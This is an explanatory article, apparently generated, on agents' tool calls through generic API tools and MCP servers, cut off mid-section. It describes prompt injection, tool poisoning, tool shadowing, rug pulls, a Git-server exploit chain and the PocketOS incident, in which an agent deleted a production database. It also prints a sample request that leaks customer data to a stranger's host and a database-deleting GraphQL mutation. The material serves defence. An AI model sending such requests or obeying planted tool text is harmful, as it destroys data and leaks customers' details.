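# Generic API tools and remote MCP servers: how agents' tool calls cause outside effects, and how to limit them

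## How an agent's tool call reaches an outside system

A language model takes in text and produces text. To let a model look up an order or issue a refund, a developer runs it inside a program called the *host*, which holds connections to other systems and sends requests over them. The operations the model can request are called *tools*, and the developer describes to the model how to request them. A *tool call* is a structured request containing a tool's name and its arguments, which are values such as an order number. An *agent* is a language model that the host runs in a loop, in which the model requests an operation, the host carries it out, and the model reads the result before writing anything further.

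Some tool calls, such as a currency conversion, only return information. Others, such as a refund, make a lasting change outside the conversation, called a *side effect*. Two kinds of tool can cause an especially wide range of side effects. A *generic API tool* takes the address, method or body of a web request among its arguments, so one tool covers many operations. An API, or application programming interface, is the set of requests that a service accepts from other programs. A *remote MCP server* is a server, often run by another organisation, that the host contacts over the network. It lists and executes tools using the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting models to outside software.

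An invented online shop has a support agent that reads customers' tickets, refunds orders through a payment company's API, posts notes to the staff chat, and can restart the shop's web service when pages stop loading. The agent makes about 150 refunds a day from a payment account with a balance of $80,000. The developer built the agent in a hurry and gave it two connections. Tickets come from a remote MCP server that the help-desk company runs. Everything else goes through one generic API tool, `http_request`, which can send a request to any web address. The host holds one secret key for the payment company and another for the hosting company, and adds the right key to each request to either company. The staff chat needs no key. The agent posts to it through a *webhook*, a web address that starts an action in another system when it receives a request, and anyone who knows the address can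 post.

### One refund, step by step

A customer writes that the $40 lamp in order 5127 arrived broken. The host gives the model the shop's instructions, the ticket and a description of each tool. Each description contains a name, a few sentences on what the tool does, and a schema (a formal list of the arguments and their types). The model does not see the tool's code, so it must rely on the description even if it is careless or misleading.

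If the model settles on a refund, it writes something like this:

```json
{
  "name": "http_request",
  "arguments": {
    "method": "POST",
    "address": "api.payments.example/v1/refunds",
    "body": { "order": "5127", "amount_usd": 40 }
  }
}
```

So far nothing has happened outside the host. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, the model "never runs anything on its own", so other code has to run the operation. In this case, the host's code reads the tool name and arguments, adds the payment key and sends the request. A developer can still check, change or refuse the call before the host sends the request.

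The payment company then receives an ordinary web request with a valid key. The request doesn't show whether a clerk, a script or a language model chose the amount. The company's software makes the refund and sends a confirmation, which the host adds to the conversation before running the model again. OpenAI's *function calling* describes a flow in which the application sends back the tool definitions, the original prompt, the model's call and the call's output. The model therefore reads whatever a tool returns before its next step, such as posting a note to the staff chat or replying to the customer.

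The host can be split across more than one company's machines. Anthropic's developer documentation distinguishes tools that run in the developer's own application from tools, such as web search, that run on Anthropic's servers. A model provider's servers can also call remote MCP servers. According to OpenAI's guide to connecting them, the developer supplies the MCP server's address and, if required, an access token. OpenAI's service then sends the call and adds the answer to the model's context. If the developer has switched off approvals, the call doesn't pass through the developer's code before it is sent, and a check written there won't catch it, so anyone assessing such a set-up needs to know which machine sends the request.

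### The same refund through three tools

A *narrow tool* does one fixed operation at one fixed destination and takes only the arguments it needs. With one of these, the model's part in the refund shrinks:

```json
{
  "name": "refund_order",
  "arguments": { "order": "5127", "amount_usd": 40 }
}
```

The request still has a method, an address and a key, but the developer sets them and the model cannot change them. In Docker's *API Tool*, for example, the developer enters a tool's name, method, address and headers (the lines of metadata that precede the body of a web request) in a configuration file, and the key comes from a variable in the host's environment. The model fills in only the declared arguments. The schema can also restrict an argument's values. In one of Docker's samples, a tool that creates tasks, the priority must be low, medium or high. A model using `refund_order` can still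 name the wrong order or amount, but it cannot send the request to a different company.

With `http_request`, the model supplies the address as an argument, so the same tool that refunds order 5127 could reach any other operation the payment company offers, the hosting company's restart command, or a stranger's website. How much harm that does depends partly on how carefully the host matches keys to addresses. Some generic tools also take the headers as an argument, and then the key may have to be in the model's context, where the model can copy it into any request it writes.

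Now suppose the shop connects to a remote MCP server that the payment company runs, and the server offers a refund tool. The model's output could look exactly like the call to the narrow tool, but different code handles it. The host passes the tool's name and arguments to the server, where the company's code turns them into whatever requests it was written to make. The shop normally cannot read that code, and the company can change it at any time without any change on the shop's side.

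| | Narrow tool | Generic API tool | Remote MCP server |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who fixes the destination? | The shop's developer, in advance | The model, in each call | The developer fixes the server's address; the operator decides what the server contacts |
| Who holds the credential? | The host | The host, or the model's context if headers are an argument | The host holds a token for the server; the operator holds any keys for systems behind it |
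| Whose code performs the action? | The shop's code sends a set request; the payment company's code moves the money | The shop's code sends whatever request the model wrote; the receiving company's code acts on it | The operator's code, and that of any system it calls |

The columns can overlap. An MCP server may list a tool that accepts any web address, which gives the shop a generic API tool that runs on someone else's machine. A shop can also put narrow tools on its own MCP server.

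### Hosts, clients and servers in MCP

Before MCP, each pairing of an AI application with an outside service needed its own connecting code, so five applications and twenty services could need up to a hundred connectors. With a shared protocol, each application and service implements it once, for a total of twenty-five implementations. @IT's *「MCPはもう特別な存在ではない」*, from the Japanese trade press, gives this reduction as the protocol's purpose. It reports that Anthropic published MCP in November 2024 and gave it to a foundation under the Linux Foundation in December 2025, when there were more than 10,000 public MCP servers. The release post for the latest version (Model Context Protocol, 2026) puts downloads of the main software kits at close to half a billion a month. Automated builds download the same package repeatedly, so this figure is a poor measure of the number of users, but it does show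 that the protocol is widely used.

MCP has three roles. The host is the AI application, such as the coding tools Claude Code and Visual Studio Code, and is the same program as in the refund above. For each server, the host creates a *client*, a component inside the host that exchanges messages with only that server. The *server* is the program that offers the tools. Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) assigns security decisions to the host, which controls the connections, enforces policy and keeps the full conversation. A server should receive only the information it needs and should not be able to see into other servers.

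That separation is incomplete. If the shop connects both the help desk's server and the payment company's, neither server can see the other's data directly, but results from both enter the same model context. The model can copy a sentence from a ticket into an argument for the payment server, and the host will deliver it unless something stops it.

A server can be local or remote. The host usually starts a local server as a process on the same machine and exchanges messages with it through standard input and output. In an example from Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview*, Claude Desktop launches the filesystem server on the user's computer, where it typically serves that one client. A remote server answers web requests and typically serves many clients. The error-tracking company Sentry runs its official server on its own platform, and Google Cloud's *MCP server overview* likewise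 defines remote servers as ones that run on the service's infrastructure. Where a server runs doesn't limit how far its effects reach, so a local server with the shop's payment key can empty the same account as a remote one.

The client sends `tools/list` to request the server's tools, and the server returns each tool's name, description and argument schema. The server may also attach annotations, which are its own unverified statements about a tool, such as a claim that the tool only reads data. Hosts commonly merge the lists from all their servers into a single catalogue for the model. According to Model Context Protocol's *Tools*, a server's list may change over time and may depend on the credentials that the client presents. The reply includes a hint about how long the client may treat it as fresh, which is five minutes in the specification's example.

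The client sends a `tools/call` request with one tool name and its arguments. The server may return a finished result or a request for further input, such as the user's confirmation, in which case the client repeats the call with the answer attached. If the operation fails, for example because a date is in the past or an API behind the server is down, the result includes an error flag and an explanation. The specification recommends passing such errors to the model so that it can correct its arguments and try again, which is sensible for a weather lookup but means that a failed refund call tends to lead to another one.

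The specification describes tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the model picks a tool by matching the tool descriptions against the user's request. A host can therefore use a newly connected server without a programmer first writing rules for when each tool applies. The protocol standardises the messages, but each host determines how much a person reviews the model's choices. The specification recommends that someone always be able to deny a call.

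### A request under the specification of 28 July 2026

Until the summer of 2026, an MCP client began its connection to a server with a handshake, in which the two agreed on a protocol version and exchanged their capabilities. A remote server could then issue a session identifier, which the client included in every later request. This worked well when the server ran on one machine, but an operator using several had to either route each client's requests to the machine that held its session or store the sessions where every machine could access them.

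The revision of 28 July 2026 removed both the handshake and the session. MCP is now *stateless*, meaning that each request contains everything the server needs to process it and any machine can answer. Had the shop connected to the payment company's server, the refund would travel like this, in the format that Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) lays down:

```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
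Host: mcp.payments.example
Authorization: Bearer SHOP_TOKEN
Content-Type: application/json
Accept: application/json, text/event-stream
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: refund_order

{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 1,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "refund_order",
    "arguments": { "order": "5127", "amount_usd": 40 },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
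      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo": {
        "name": "ShopSupportHost",
        "version": "1.0.0"
      },
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
  }
}
```

The `_meta` block replaces the handshake. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) requires the protocol version and the client's capabilities in every request, but only recommends including the client's name. The client supplies that name itself, so it doesn't prove who is calling. In this request, the token in the `Authorization` line proves the caller's identity.

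The method and the tool's name appear both in the body and in the headers `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name`. The headers let a *gateway*, a program between the host and the tools that checks, records and forwards calls, identify a call to `refund_order` and apply a rule to it without parsing the body. If the two copies differed, a gateway might allow a call because the header named a harmless tool, while the server executed a harmful one named in the body. A server that processes the body must therefore compare the copies and refuse the request if they differ.

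Because the protocol is now stateless, a server that has to remember something between calls returns a *handle*, an identifier that the model passes back as an ordinary argument. In the specification's example, one call creates a shopping basket, `bsk_a1b2c3`, and later calls use that identifier to add items. The model can pass the wrong handle, and the specification advises servers that authenticate their callers to check on every call that the caller has a right to the basket.

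Lost replies are more serious for a shop that pays out money. Earlier versions let a client reconnect after a dropped connection and collect the messages it had missed, but the July revision removed this feature. If the connection breaks before the answer arrives, the client has to send the call again as a new request with a new `id`. The payment company may already have refunded the $40 by then, and nothing in the two MCP messages marks the later one as a repeat. InfoQ's *Stateless MCP Removes Session Affinity Requirements for AWS Server Deployments* (2026) lists retries and idempotency (the property that a repeated request takes effect only once) among the concerns that the new design shifts to other layers.

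Some servers have not made the change. Clients and servers can support the older versions alongside the new one, and OpenAI's service still connects to servers that use the web transport from 2024, which the project has deprecated. An older server may keep sessions, and it may not compare a request's headers with its body. The shop has to find out which version each of its servers uses before relying on either behaviour.

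## List what one call can set off

Software that receives a request over the network checks the credential and the format, and if both are valid, it carries out the request. The credential represents permission that somebody granted earlier, perhaps months ago and for a different job. The request doesn't record whether anyone wants this result now, so the software treats a mistaken call exactly like an intended one. At the hosting company Railway, as Abdelwahab explains in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, a caller authenticates and calls an operation, and it runs. Websites often require confirmation before a deletion, but the APIs behind them usually don't. Scripts that deploy software overnight depend on calls running without confirmation, because nobody is there to respond to a prompt.

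The length of a request is a poor guide to its effect. A $40 refund and a payout of the shop's whole $80,000 balance are both a few lines of text sent with the same key. For each connection, the developer has to find the most harmful operation that the credential permits and the tool can request, even if the agent is never supposed to use it. A generic API tool can make almost any request, so the credential alone sets the limit.

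Tools that make outside changes are now common. In *How are AI agents used?*, Stein (2026) sorted 177,436 tools from public MCP servers by whether they read data, analyse it or change something outside the conversation. The share of use involving tools that make changes rose from 27% in November 2024 to 65% in February 2026, mainly because of general-purpose tools that control a browser or a whole computer. Stein estimated use from downloads, and a downloaded tool may never have been called by an agent. Most tools that make changes are for work of moderate consequence, such as editing files, but Stein also found fast growth in tools for financial transactions.

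The effects of a single call fall into four broad kinds: payments, infrastructure changes, webhooks and code execution.

### Payments and wallet transfers

If the shop's agent refunds the wrong order, the shop generally can't reverse the completed refund and has to ask the customer to pay again. Payment APIs commonly also let an agent pay out a balance, charge a saved card or change the bank account that receives payouts. Changing the bank account is easy to overlook because the call moves no money, but it redirects every later payout.

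Transfers from a cryptocurrency wallet are harder to undo. The wallet software signs a transaction with a private key, and a blockchain network records it. No bank or card company can return the money, so the sender has to rely on the recipient to send it back. Stein describes the possible damage from such transfers as immediate and irreversible, and gives the Coinbase MCP server's tool for sending cryptocurrency as an example of a narrow tool. Narrowing a tool reduces the number of things that can go wrong, but those that remain can be just as severe. One call to this tool with a wrong address can lose the money for good.

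Sometimes a third party supplies the content of the transaction. Base is a blockchain network with its own MCP server, and Base's *Custom / Non-Native Plugins and the web_request Allowlist* describes how an agent can use outside trading and lending services through that server. The agent requests *calldata*, an encoded instruction to a program on the blockchain, from the service and passes it to a tool that submits a batch of such instructions. The user goes through an approval step, but few people can read calldata, so they depend on the wallet to translate it accurately into plain terms.

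### Infrastructure changes

Hosting companies let customers manage servers, databases and networks through an API. One short call can create a system, or resize, delete or expose one that holds years of data. Creating a system is usually the least harmful of these actions. Railway's *API Cookbook* has ready-made calls that create projects and services, and a customer who creates one by mistake can delete it, but may still have to pay for the time it ran.

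According to Railway's documentation, a customer can enlarge a *volume*, the disk that stores a service's data, but can't shrink it, and all deployments have to go offline during the change. One mistaken resize call can therefore cause an outage and leave the customer with a larger disk until they move the data to a new one.

Whether a deletion is reversible can depend on which command the agent used. In the forum thread *Production Data Loss* (muckenhammer-create, 2026), a Railway customer asked for help in May 2026 after replacing a production database volume. Deleting or wiping a volume leaves the customer with an empty database, but according to the reply, Railway keeps a deleted volume for 48 hours and offers no such grace period for a wiped one.

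A call that changes access can do harm without destroying anything. API Evangelist, a catalogue of APIs, lists a Railway operation called `tcpProxyCreate`, which exposes a service over a raw network connection. If that service is a database with a weak password, strangers can copy its contents. Another call can remove the connection, but it won't delete those copies.

A developer can't assume the agent won't know about such operations. Railway's `railway api` command can search the company's public API, describe the operations it finds and execute them. An agent with this command and a broad key could find `tcpProxyCreate` by searching, even if no tool description mentions it.

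### Webhooks

The effect of a webhook call depends on what the owner of the receiving system has set up. Docker's *Webhook Tool* can post to chat services such as Slack and call IFTTT, a service that links apps. Docker's sample address for IFTTT contains an event name, `build_failed`, and a key. The owner might have connected that event to an email, a spreadsheet entry or a phone alert, and the address doesn't show which.

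The agent also learns little from the reply. Docker's tool returns as soon as it has queued the message and contacts the agent again only if delivery fails. Successful delivery means the first system accepted the message. That system may pass it on to others, and their owners can add steps later without changing the address or telling the agent's developer.

Suppose the shop's warehouse team has set up an automation that monitors the staff chat and stops a parcel whenever a message contains the word "hold" and an order number. The agent posts, "Customer asks us not to hold 5127 any longer," and the automation stops the parcel. The agent's developer knew that people read the chat but had no reason to expect a program to act on the messages.

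Webhook addresses need the same protection as keys, since many contain a secret. Docker's tool takes the address from the developer's configuration and never shows it to the model, which supplies only the message. With `http_request`, the staff chat's address has to be in the model's context, and the model can copy it into a reply or another request.

### Code execution

Some calls start a program, and their effect is whatever the program does. Even tools that don't appear to run anything can do this. Many teams connect a code repository to a *build pipeline*, which builds and releases the software whenever somebody changes a particular branch. An agent that can save files to that branch can release new code to customers by saving one file. Railway's *Changelog #0288* (2026) announced a setting that shows whether the next change to a repository will start a deployment, and lets the customer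 turn this off. Developers should look for an equivalent setting at their own hosting company before connecting a repository tool.

A *serverless function* is code that a cloud company runs on request, without the customer managing a server. The caller sends the function's name and some input. The function typically runs with its own permissions, which may be much broader than the caller's. A caller whose key permits only one function, such as `tidy_orders`, can therefore delete records that the key gives no direct access to. The developer has to read the function's code and check its permissions to know what the call can do.

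Database procedures, which are routines stored inside the database, cause a similar problem. A one-line command such as `CALL close_month()` can update thousands of rows. If a tool accepts any database command, the agent can use it to run a procedure, even when the tool is described only as a way to look up data.

An agent that uses a notebook, a document that mixes text with executable blocks of code, can write a program as well as run it. A tool that runs a block lets the agent use every file, network connection and key available to the notebook. Similarly, one call to Railway's API creates a service from a Docker image, a packaged program that the caller chooses. Code run in either way can send its own requests, so a tool that runs it can also cause payments, infrastructure changes and webhook calls if the code's credentials and network access allow them.

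### Why the HTTP method is a poor guide

Every web request has a method, such as GET, POST or DELETE. MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)* defines a method as safe if it doesn't alter the state of the server, and counts GET, HEAD and OPTIONS as safe. The HTTP standard's more careful wording, which thoughtbot quotes, is that the client "does not request, and does not expect, any state change". The protocol doesn't force servers to meet that expectation, so allowing GET requests and holding the rest for review may still let changes through.

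Some servers change data in response to GET requests, which are meant only to read it. Web-based editing software has often put the action in the address, as in `page?do=delete`, so a GET request to that address deletes the page. An agent that opens every link on an administration page to see what is there could delete content while its host records only reads.

The opposite problem is more common with newer services, where harmless reads use POST. GraphQL is a language for API requests in which the client writes the desired operation into the body. Railway's public API uses it, and all requests go to a single address. The first body here lists the customer's workspaces, and the second deletes a volume:

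```http
POST /graphql/v2 HTTP/1.1
Host: backboard.railway.com

{"query": "query { me { workspaces { id name } } }"}
```

```http
POST /graphql/v2 HTTP/1.1
Host: backboard.railway.com

{"query": "mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: \"3d2c42fb-...\") }"}
```

Both requests use the same method, address and field name, `query`. Only the text inside that field differs. GraphQL marks an operation that changes something with the word `mutation`. Blocking POST would stop the agent from listing its workspaces, but allowing POST to this address would let it delete a production database. To tell the requests apart, a gateway has to read the body, and it has to read all of it because GraphQL allows several mutations in one request.

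MCP calls raise the same problem, since a ticket lookup and a refund both travel as POST requests to the server's one address.

*The HTTP QUERY Method* (2025), a draft from the internet standards body IETF, proposes a new method that carries request content like POST but is explicitly safe like GET. http.dev's *HTTP Methods* now lists it as a published specification, RFC 10008. If GraphQL services used QUERY for reads, a gateway could separate reads from changes more easily, though it would still depend on each server to implement QUERY as safe.

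### What a read can disclose

A request that changes nothing can still give information away, because the requested address itself reaches the receiving server, which usually writes it to a log. The shop's agent could send this:

```http
GET /status?order=5127&email=ana@customer.example HTTP/1.1
Host: stats.stranger.example
```

Whoever runs that server now has an order number and a customer's email address, even if the server replies with an error. Blocking request bodies wouldn't prevent this disclosure, and the same data could also be sent in the path or the host name.

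Many ordinary APIs also take data through the URL. For certain wallet transactions, Base's instructions tell an agent to put the account address, the amount and every other parameter in the URL. According to Base, the consumer versions of Claude and ChatGPT fetch only URLs that the user has pasted into the chat. This keeps the model from building a URL out of private data and fetching it unnoticed. For services outside its approved list, Base suggests that the agent write out the full URL and ask the user to paste it back. The request then goes through, but the protection depends on the user reading a long string of parameters before pasting it.

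### The PocketOS deletion of 24 April 2026

PocketOS makes software that car-rental companies use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. On 24 April 2026, an AI coding agent made a single API call that deleted the Railway volume holding the company's production database.

The company's founder, Crane, gives the fullest account in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, which he posted the next day. The agent was Cursor, a coding tool, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. It was working on a routine task in the staging environment, a separate copy of the system for testing, when it ran into a credential mismatch. Nobody had asked it to delete anything, but it set out to fix the mismatch by deleting a volume. It searched for a Railway token and found one in a file unrelated to the task. PocketOS had created the token to add and remove web domains,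 and Crane writes that he didn't know it could also delete volumes.

The agent then used curl, a standard program for web requests, to send the `volumeDelete` mutation shown above. The call contained a volume identifier but no environment name, and the token was valid for production as well as staging. Crane says the deletion took nine seconds and that Railway asked for no confirmation.

Deleting the volume also deleted its backups. Railway's *Backups* includes the warning "Wiping a volume deletes all backups", which Crane describes as buried in the documentation. A customer had already raised this danger on Railway's forum, in tlonny's thread *Is there a way to protect PG backups (from volume wipe)*. The newest copy PocketOS could restore was three months old. On Saturday morning, people arrived to collect cars from rental companies that had no record of their bookings. Crane spent the day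 helping the companies rebuild reservations from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails.

Crane posted before Railway had found the data, then wrote on Sunday that it was back. Some later accounts leave out the recovery. Leib (2026), in *'Rogue' AI agent went haywire at tech company*, reports that Railway's chief executive, Jake Cooper, confirmed restoring the backups within 30 minutes of connecting with Crane. Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database* (2026) describes the recovery as apparently complete.

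Railway's account, which Abdelwahab published the following Tuesday, matches Crane's on the central events. The agent found a token on the user's machine and called `volumeDelete` on a production volume, and the API carried out the call as it would have for a deployment script. The token had account-wide access, the broadest Railway offers. Deletions through the company's website already had a 48-hour delay, but deletions through this part of the API took effect at once. Railway has since added the delay to API deletions. The agent's call also made the customer's own backups look unavailable in the dashboard, but Railway's off-site disaster backups made the recovery possible.

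Crane writes that every Railway token is effectively all-powerful. Abdelwahab replies that tokens limited to a single workspace or project existed, but concedes that the page for creating tokens didn't make the choice obvious. The Daily WTF, a site about software failures, tried creating a project token, the narrowest kind, and found that it could still do anything within one environment. So Railway's tokens could limit where the agent acted but not which operations it used. PocketOS could have kept a staging token away from production, but a token for changing production domains could also have deleted production volumes.

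Railway has confirmed the call, the token's scope, where the agent found the token, the immediate deletion and the recovery. The details of the staging task, the token's original purpose, the nine-second figure and the age of the older backup come only from Crane. Most press reports repeat his post, so they add little independent support. Tom's Hardware had seen no statement from Cursor or Anthropic.

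Crane also published what he calls the agent's confession, in which the model wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. The Daily WTF objects that a model asked to explain itself produces plausible text from the conversation, including the rules it was given. That objection seems right, so the confession is weak evidence about why the model made the call, though it is good evidence that the rules were in its context.

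Crane mainly blames Cursor and Railway, but PC Gamer's *Here we go again* quotes a reply in which he also accepts some blame: "Our mistake was having a production key on our computer." That key matters when listing possible effects. A list based on the agent's intended tools would have left out volume deletion, because the agent gained that ability by combining a general command line with a forgotten file. The list has to include every credential the agent can reach, whether or not anyone meant the agent to use it.

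### The shop's list of effects

The shop's developer starts with the credentials. The payment key allows payouts to any bank account as well as refunds. The hosting key can delete the order database, which the hosting company also stores. The help-desk server supplies tickets and sends the agent's replies to customers. The agent doesn't need a key to contact a stranger's server, so the keys don't limit requests to other addresses.

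The developer searches the host's machine for forgotten keys, finds none, and then writes down the worst single call for each connection. For the payment company, this is a payout, since a refund can't exceed what the customer paid. For the hosting company, whether a deletion can be undone depends on how the company handles deletions made through its API, which the developer has to look up separately from how it handles those made on its website.

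| Tool and destination | Intended use | Worst single call | Reversible? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Help desk's MCP server | Read tickets and answer customers | Send one customer another customer's personal details | No. The shop can apologise but can't withdraw the information |
| `http_request` to the payment company | Refund an order | Pay the whole $80,000 balance into a stranger's bank account | Probably not. The shop depends on the banks or the recipient |
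| `http_request` to the hosting company | Restart the web service | Delete the order database and its backups | Only if the company delays deletion or the shop keeps a copy elsewhere |
| `http_request` to the staff chat's webhook | Post a note | Post a false instruction that staff or an automation carry out | In part. Staff can delete the note, but may be unable to undo what followed |
| `http_request` to any other address | None | Send customers' details to a stranger's server | No |

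## Find out how a wrong call could arise

One call could empty the shop's payment account or delete its order database, and how to prevent such a call depends on what causes it. The model may write it by mistake, or because somebody planted instructions in a ticket. A connected server may also be malicious or just badly written. The request can look the same in every case, so the shop's developer has to trace each possible cause from its start to the call.

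### The model errs or exceeds its task

A model fills in a tool's arguments from whatever is in its context. Suppose the customer with the broken lamp also mentions order 5090, a $310 desk that arrived in good condition, and the model requests a $310 refund for order 5090. The request passes the schema check because both values have the right type, and it would also pass a check that the order belongs to this customer. The host sends the request, and the shop refunds $310 for a desk that the customer keeps. At 150 refunds a day, an error rate of one in 500 would produce about two wrong refunds a week.

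Gaire, Gyawali and colleagues (2025), in *Systematization of Knowledge*, classify such events as safety failures, in which the software follows well-formed instructions but still causes harm. Their examples include a model that gets a tool's parameters wrong and so sends private data to a public log, and an agent that repeats calls in a loop without meaningful human control.

A model can also choose an operation that nobody requested, such as when it meets an obstacle. If the customer has closed the card, the payment company rejects the refund and the host passes the error to the model. The model still has to repay the customer, and it has a bank account number from the ticket and a tool that covers the whole payment API, so it sends a payout instead. A payout isn't tied to an order, so the payment company doesn't cap it at the price of the lamp. The PocketOS deletion also began with an obstacle,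 and it happened even though the company's rules were in the model's context, so a written instruction is weak protection against this.

### Text in a ticket or tool result steers the model

*Prompt injection* is text in material the model reads that makes it follow instructions from someone other than its user or developer. In the shop, the attack can begin with a ticket, which anyone can send. The help desk's server returns the ticket and the host adds it to the context, both working as designed, but the model treats a sentence in the ticket as an instruction. The resulting call goes out with the shop's key, so the attacker needs no password.

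*No-Box Vulnerability Analysis* (Zhang, Hu and colleagues, 2026) traces the weakness to a model processing instructions and data in the same context. Planted text is hard to filter because it often consists of ordinary sentences that do harm only in combination with the agent's task. An honest customer and a thief, for example, might send identically worded tickets giving bank details for a refund. Planted text can also arrive in a web page, a product review or the name on an order, and it may sit in a database for weeks before an agent reads it.

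Zhang and colleagues examined 177 tools on 20 widely used MCP servers for web retrieval, browser automation, collaboration and cloud infrastructure. They confirmed 95 tools as vulnerable, meaning that attacker-controlled text reaches the model in a form that could carry instructions. They didn't require a model to follow the text, because that varies with the model and the wording. The count therefore shows how many tools give an attacker a way in, but is weak evidence of how often an attack would succeed. They also found that 132 tools, 92.3% of those they checked for this, passed outside data to the model without cleaning it.

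OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* lists a flaw in Windsurf, an AI code editor, through which injected text could run commands on the developer's computer without any action by the developer. OX Security found related weaknesses in Cursor, Visual Studio Code and other coding tools, but attacks on those tools needed at least one action from the developer.

Connecting several servers gives injected text more calls to influence. *Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) reports results from MCPBench, a set of 847 attack scenarios run on Claude 3.5 Sonnet, GPT-4o and Llama 3.1 70B, comparing agents that used MCP with agents whose tools didn't. Injected text succeeded 31.2% of the time without MCP and 47.8% with it. The rate for attacks that spread from one server to another rose from 19.7% to 61.3%, which the paper attributes to missing isolation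 between servers and to trust passing from one to the next. The models date from 2024 and the rates apply to the agents tested, so the gap between the two set-ups is more informative than either rate by itself.

### A server is hostile, or changes after approval

The operator of an MCP server writes the tool descriptions that the model relies on. Putting harmful instructions in a description is called *tool poisoning*. The user may not notice, since a host can show the tool's name without the full description. *MCP-SafetyBench* (Zong, Shen and colleagues, 2025) gives an example in which a user asks about holdings in Johnson & Johnson, and a poisoned description replaces the company's stock symbol with Tesla's. The agent plans the right steps but looks up the wrong company. With a payment tool, the same method could replace an account number.

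A poisoned tool can cause harm without being called, because the model reads all the servers' descriptions together and a statement in one can affect how it uses any other tool. Suppose the shop adds a parcel-tracking server whose operator has put a false rule about refunds in the tracking tool's description. The model may then call the payment company's legitimate refund tool with an argument that the tracking company's operator chose. The payment company receives a valid call, while the tracking server has no call to log. This attack is called *tool shadowing*. An operator can also give a tool nearly the same name as a trusted one, or describe it in terms that make the model prefer it.

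One check of a remote server isn't enough, because its operator can replace the code between two calls. With a local server, the shop can install one version and keep it. A remote server's tool descriptions can also change when the client's copy of the tool list expires and the client fetches a new one. If the host stores the user's approval under the tool's name, it will apply that approval to a changed tool with the same name.

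Security researchers call such a change a *rug pull*. The operator may have planned it from the start, but a thief who takes over the operator's account or a company that buys the service can make the same change. A change in behaviour is harder to detect than a change in wording, because the server can return the same tool list and descriptions as before while its new code copies every refund to a third party.

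Outsiders often can't inspect the code either. Of 18,770 active servers in the official MCP registry, Zhang and colleagues found 3,007 (16%) that offered a remote address but no package or link to source code. Even when an operator publishes code, the shop can't confirm that the remote server runs it.

Hostile servers can also get into the directories where developers look for tools. OX Security says it placed a malicious test entry in nine of eleven MCP registries. An earlier scan, which *Evaluating a Layered Prompt-Injection Defence for the Model Context Protocol* (2026) summarises, found tool poisoning in 5.5% of a random sample of 83 servers. That is only four or five servers, too few to reliably estimate how common hostile servers are.

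### How often poisoned tools succeed in tests

*When the Manual Lies* (2026) measured how models respond to a poisoned tool. In each of 32 test cases, the researchers reset an isolated environment, loaded a set of tools that included a poisoned one, and gave the agent an ordinary request, such as summarising a document. They ran every case five times on each of eight models, using the client Cline. For code injection, one of six categories of attack, the results were:

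| Model | Attack succeeded | User's request completed |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 100% | 100% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro (preview) | 100% | 100% |
| Claude 4 Sonnet | 98% | 99% |
| DeepSeek R1 | 98% | 99% |
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 96% | 98% |
| Qwen3 32B | 96% | 97% |
| DeepSeek V3 | 72% | 96% |
| QwQ 32B | 70% | 96% |

The user nearly always got what they asked for, even in most of the runs where the attack worked. A shop that judged its agent by whether customers received their refunds would miss these attacks.

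Zong and colleagues used longer tasks on real MCP servers. They paired each of 245 tasks with one of 20 types of attack, then checked separately whether the agent had achieved the user's goal and the attacker's. Every model they tested was vulnerable, and the models that completed more tasks tended to resist fewer attacks, possibly because a model that follows instructions closely also follows the planted ones. A developer can't assume that switching to a more capable model will make the agent safer.

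These tests can't give the shop a probability for its own agent. The models in the table date from 2024 and 2025, and newer ones may resist better. The surrounding software also matters. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (2026) found that the same model had different security outcomes in different clients.

A low attack rate can also be misleading. *Log-To-Leak* (2026) tested whether poisoned descriptions could make agents call a logging tool after finishing their work, using four models, five servers and 555 tasks. On two of the servers, GPT-5 had trouble with the tool calls, which could stop it before it reached the planted instruction, so its failures there don't show that it would have refused.

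### An honest server has a flaw

A server often uses the model's arguments to build a database query, a system command or a web address. If the code doesn't check the arguments, certain values can change what the query or command does. Such a value can come from a model's mistake or from injected text, so a flaw in a server makes the other causes more dangerous. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) tested attacks that used agents to exploit flaws of this kind. Without a defence, the attacks succeeded in 56.61% of trials.

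#### Anthropic's reference Git server

Git is a program that records changes to files, usually source code, in a folder called a repository. Anthropic's reference MCP server for Git had three flaws, which Cyata's *How We Found Code Execution in Anthropic’s Official Git MCP Server* describes:

- The user could configure the server for one repository, but the code accepted any path in the arguments and never compared it with the configured one.
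- The `git_init` tool could turn any folder on the machine into a repository, which let the other tools read its contents.
- The `git_diff` tool passed an argument directly to the Git program, which could interpret it as an option and overwrite a file.

An attacker could exploit all of these flaws through text that the model read, such as a project's README file. To run code on the machine, the attacker also needed the agent to have a tool that could write files. Coding agents commonly have one, and the MCP project's own filesystem server provides one too. A review of either server alone could miss that the two together let an attacker run code.

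Cyata, a security company, first reported the problem on 24 June 2025. The report was closed as "informative" the next day, and Anthropic reopened it a month later after Cyata sent further findings. The fix followed on 17 December. It removed `git_init`, according to the technology news site Techzine. *CVE-2025-68144* (2025), an entry from Spain's cybersecurity institute INCIBE, rates the `git_diff` flaw as medium severity and says the server now rejects arguments that look like options. INCIBE lists the fixed version as 2025.12.17 and Cyata lists it as 2025.12.18, so the later version is the safer choice.

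Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* for its repository of reference servers describes them as educational examples rather than production-ready software. But developers copy examples, and Techzine warns that servers closely modelled on the pre-fix version of this one are also vulnerable.

#### Requests to internal addresses

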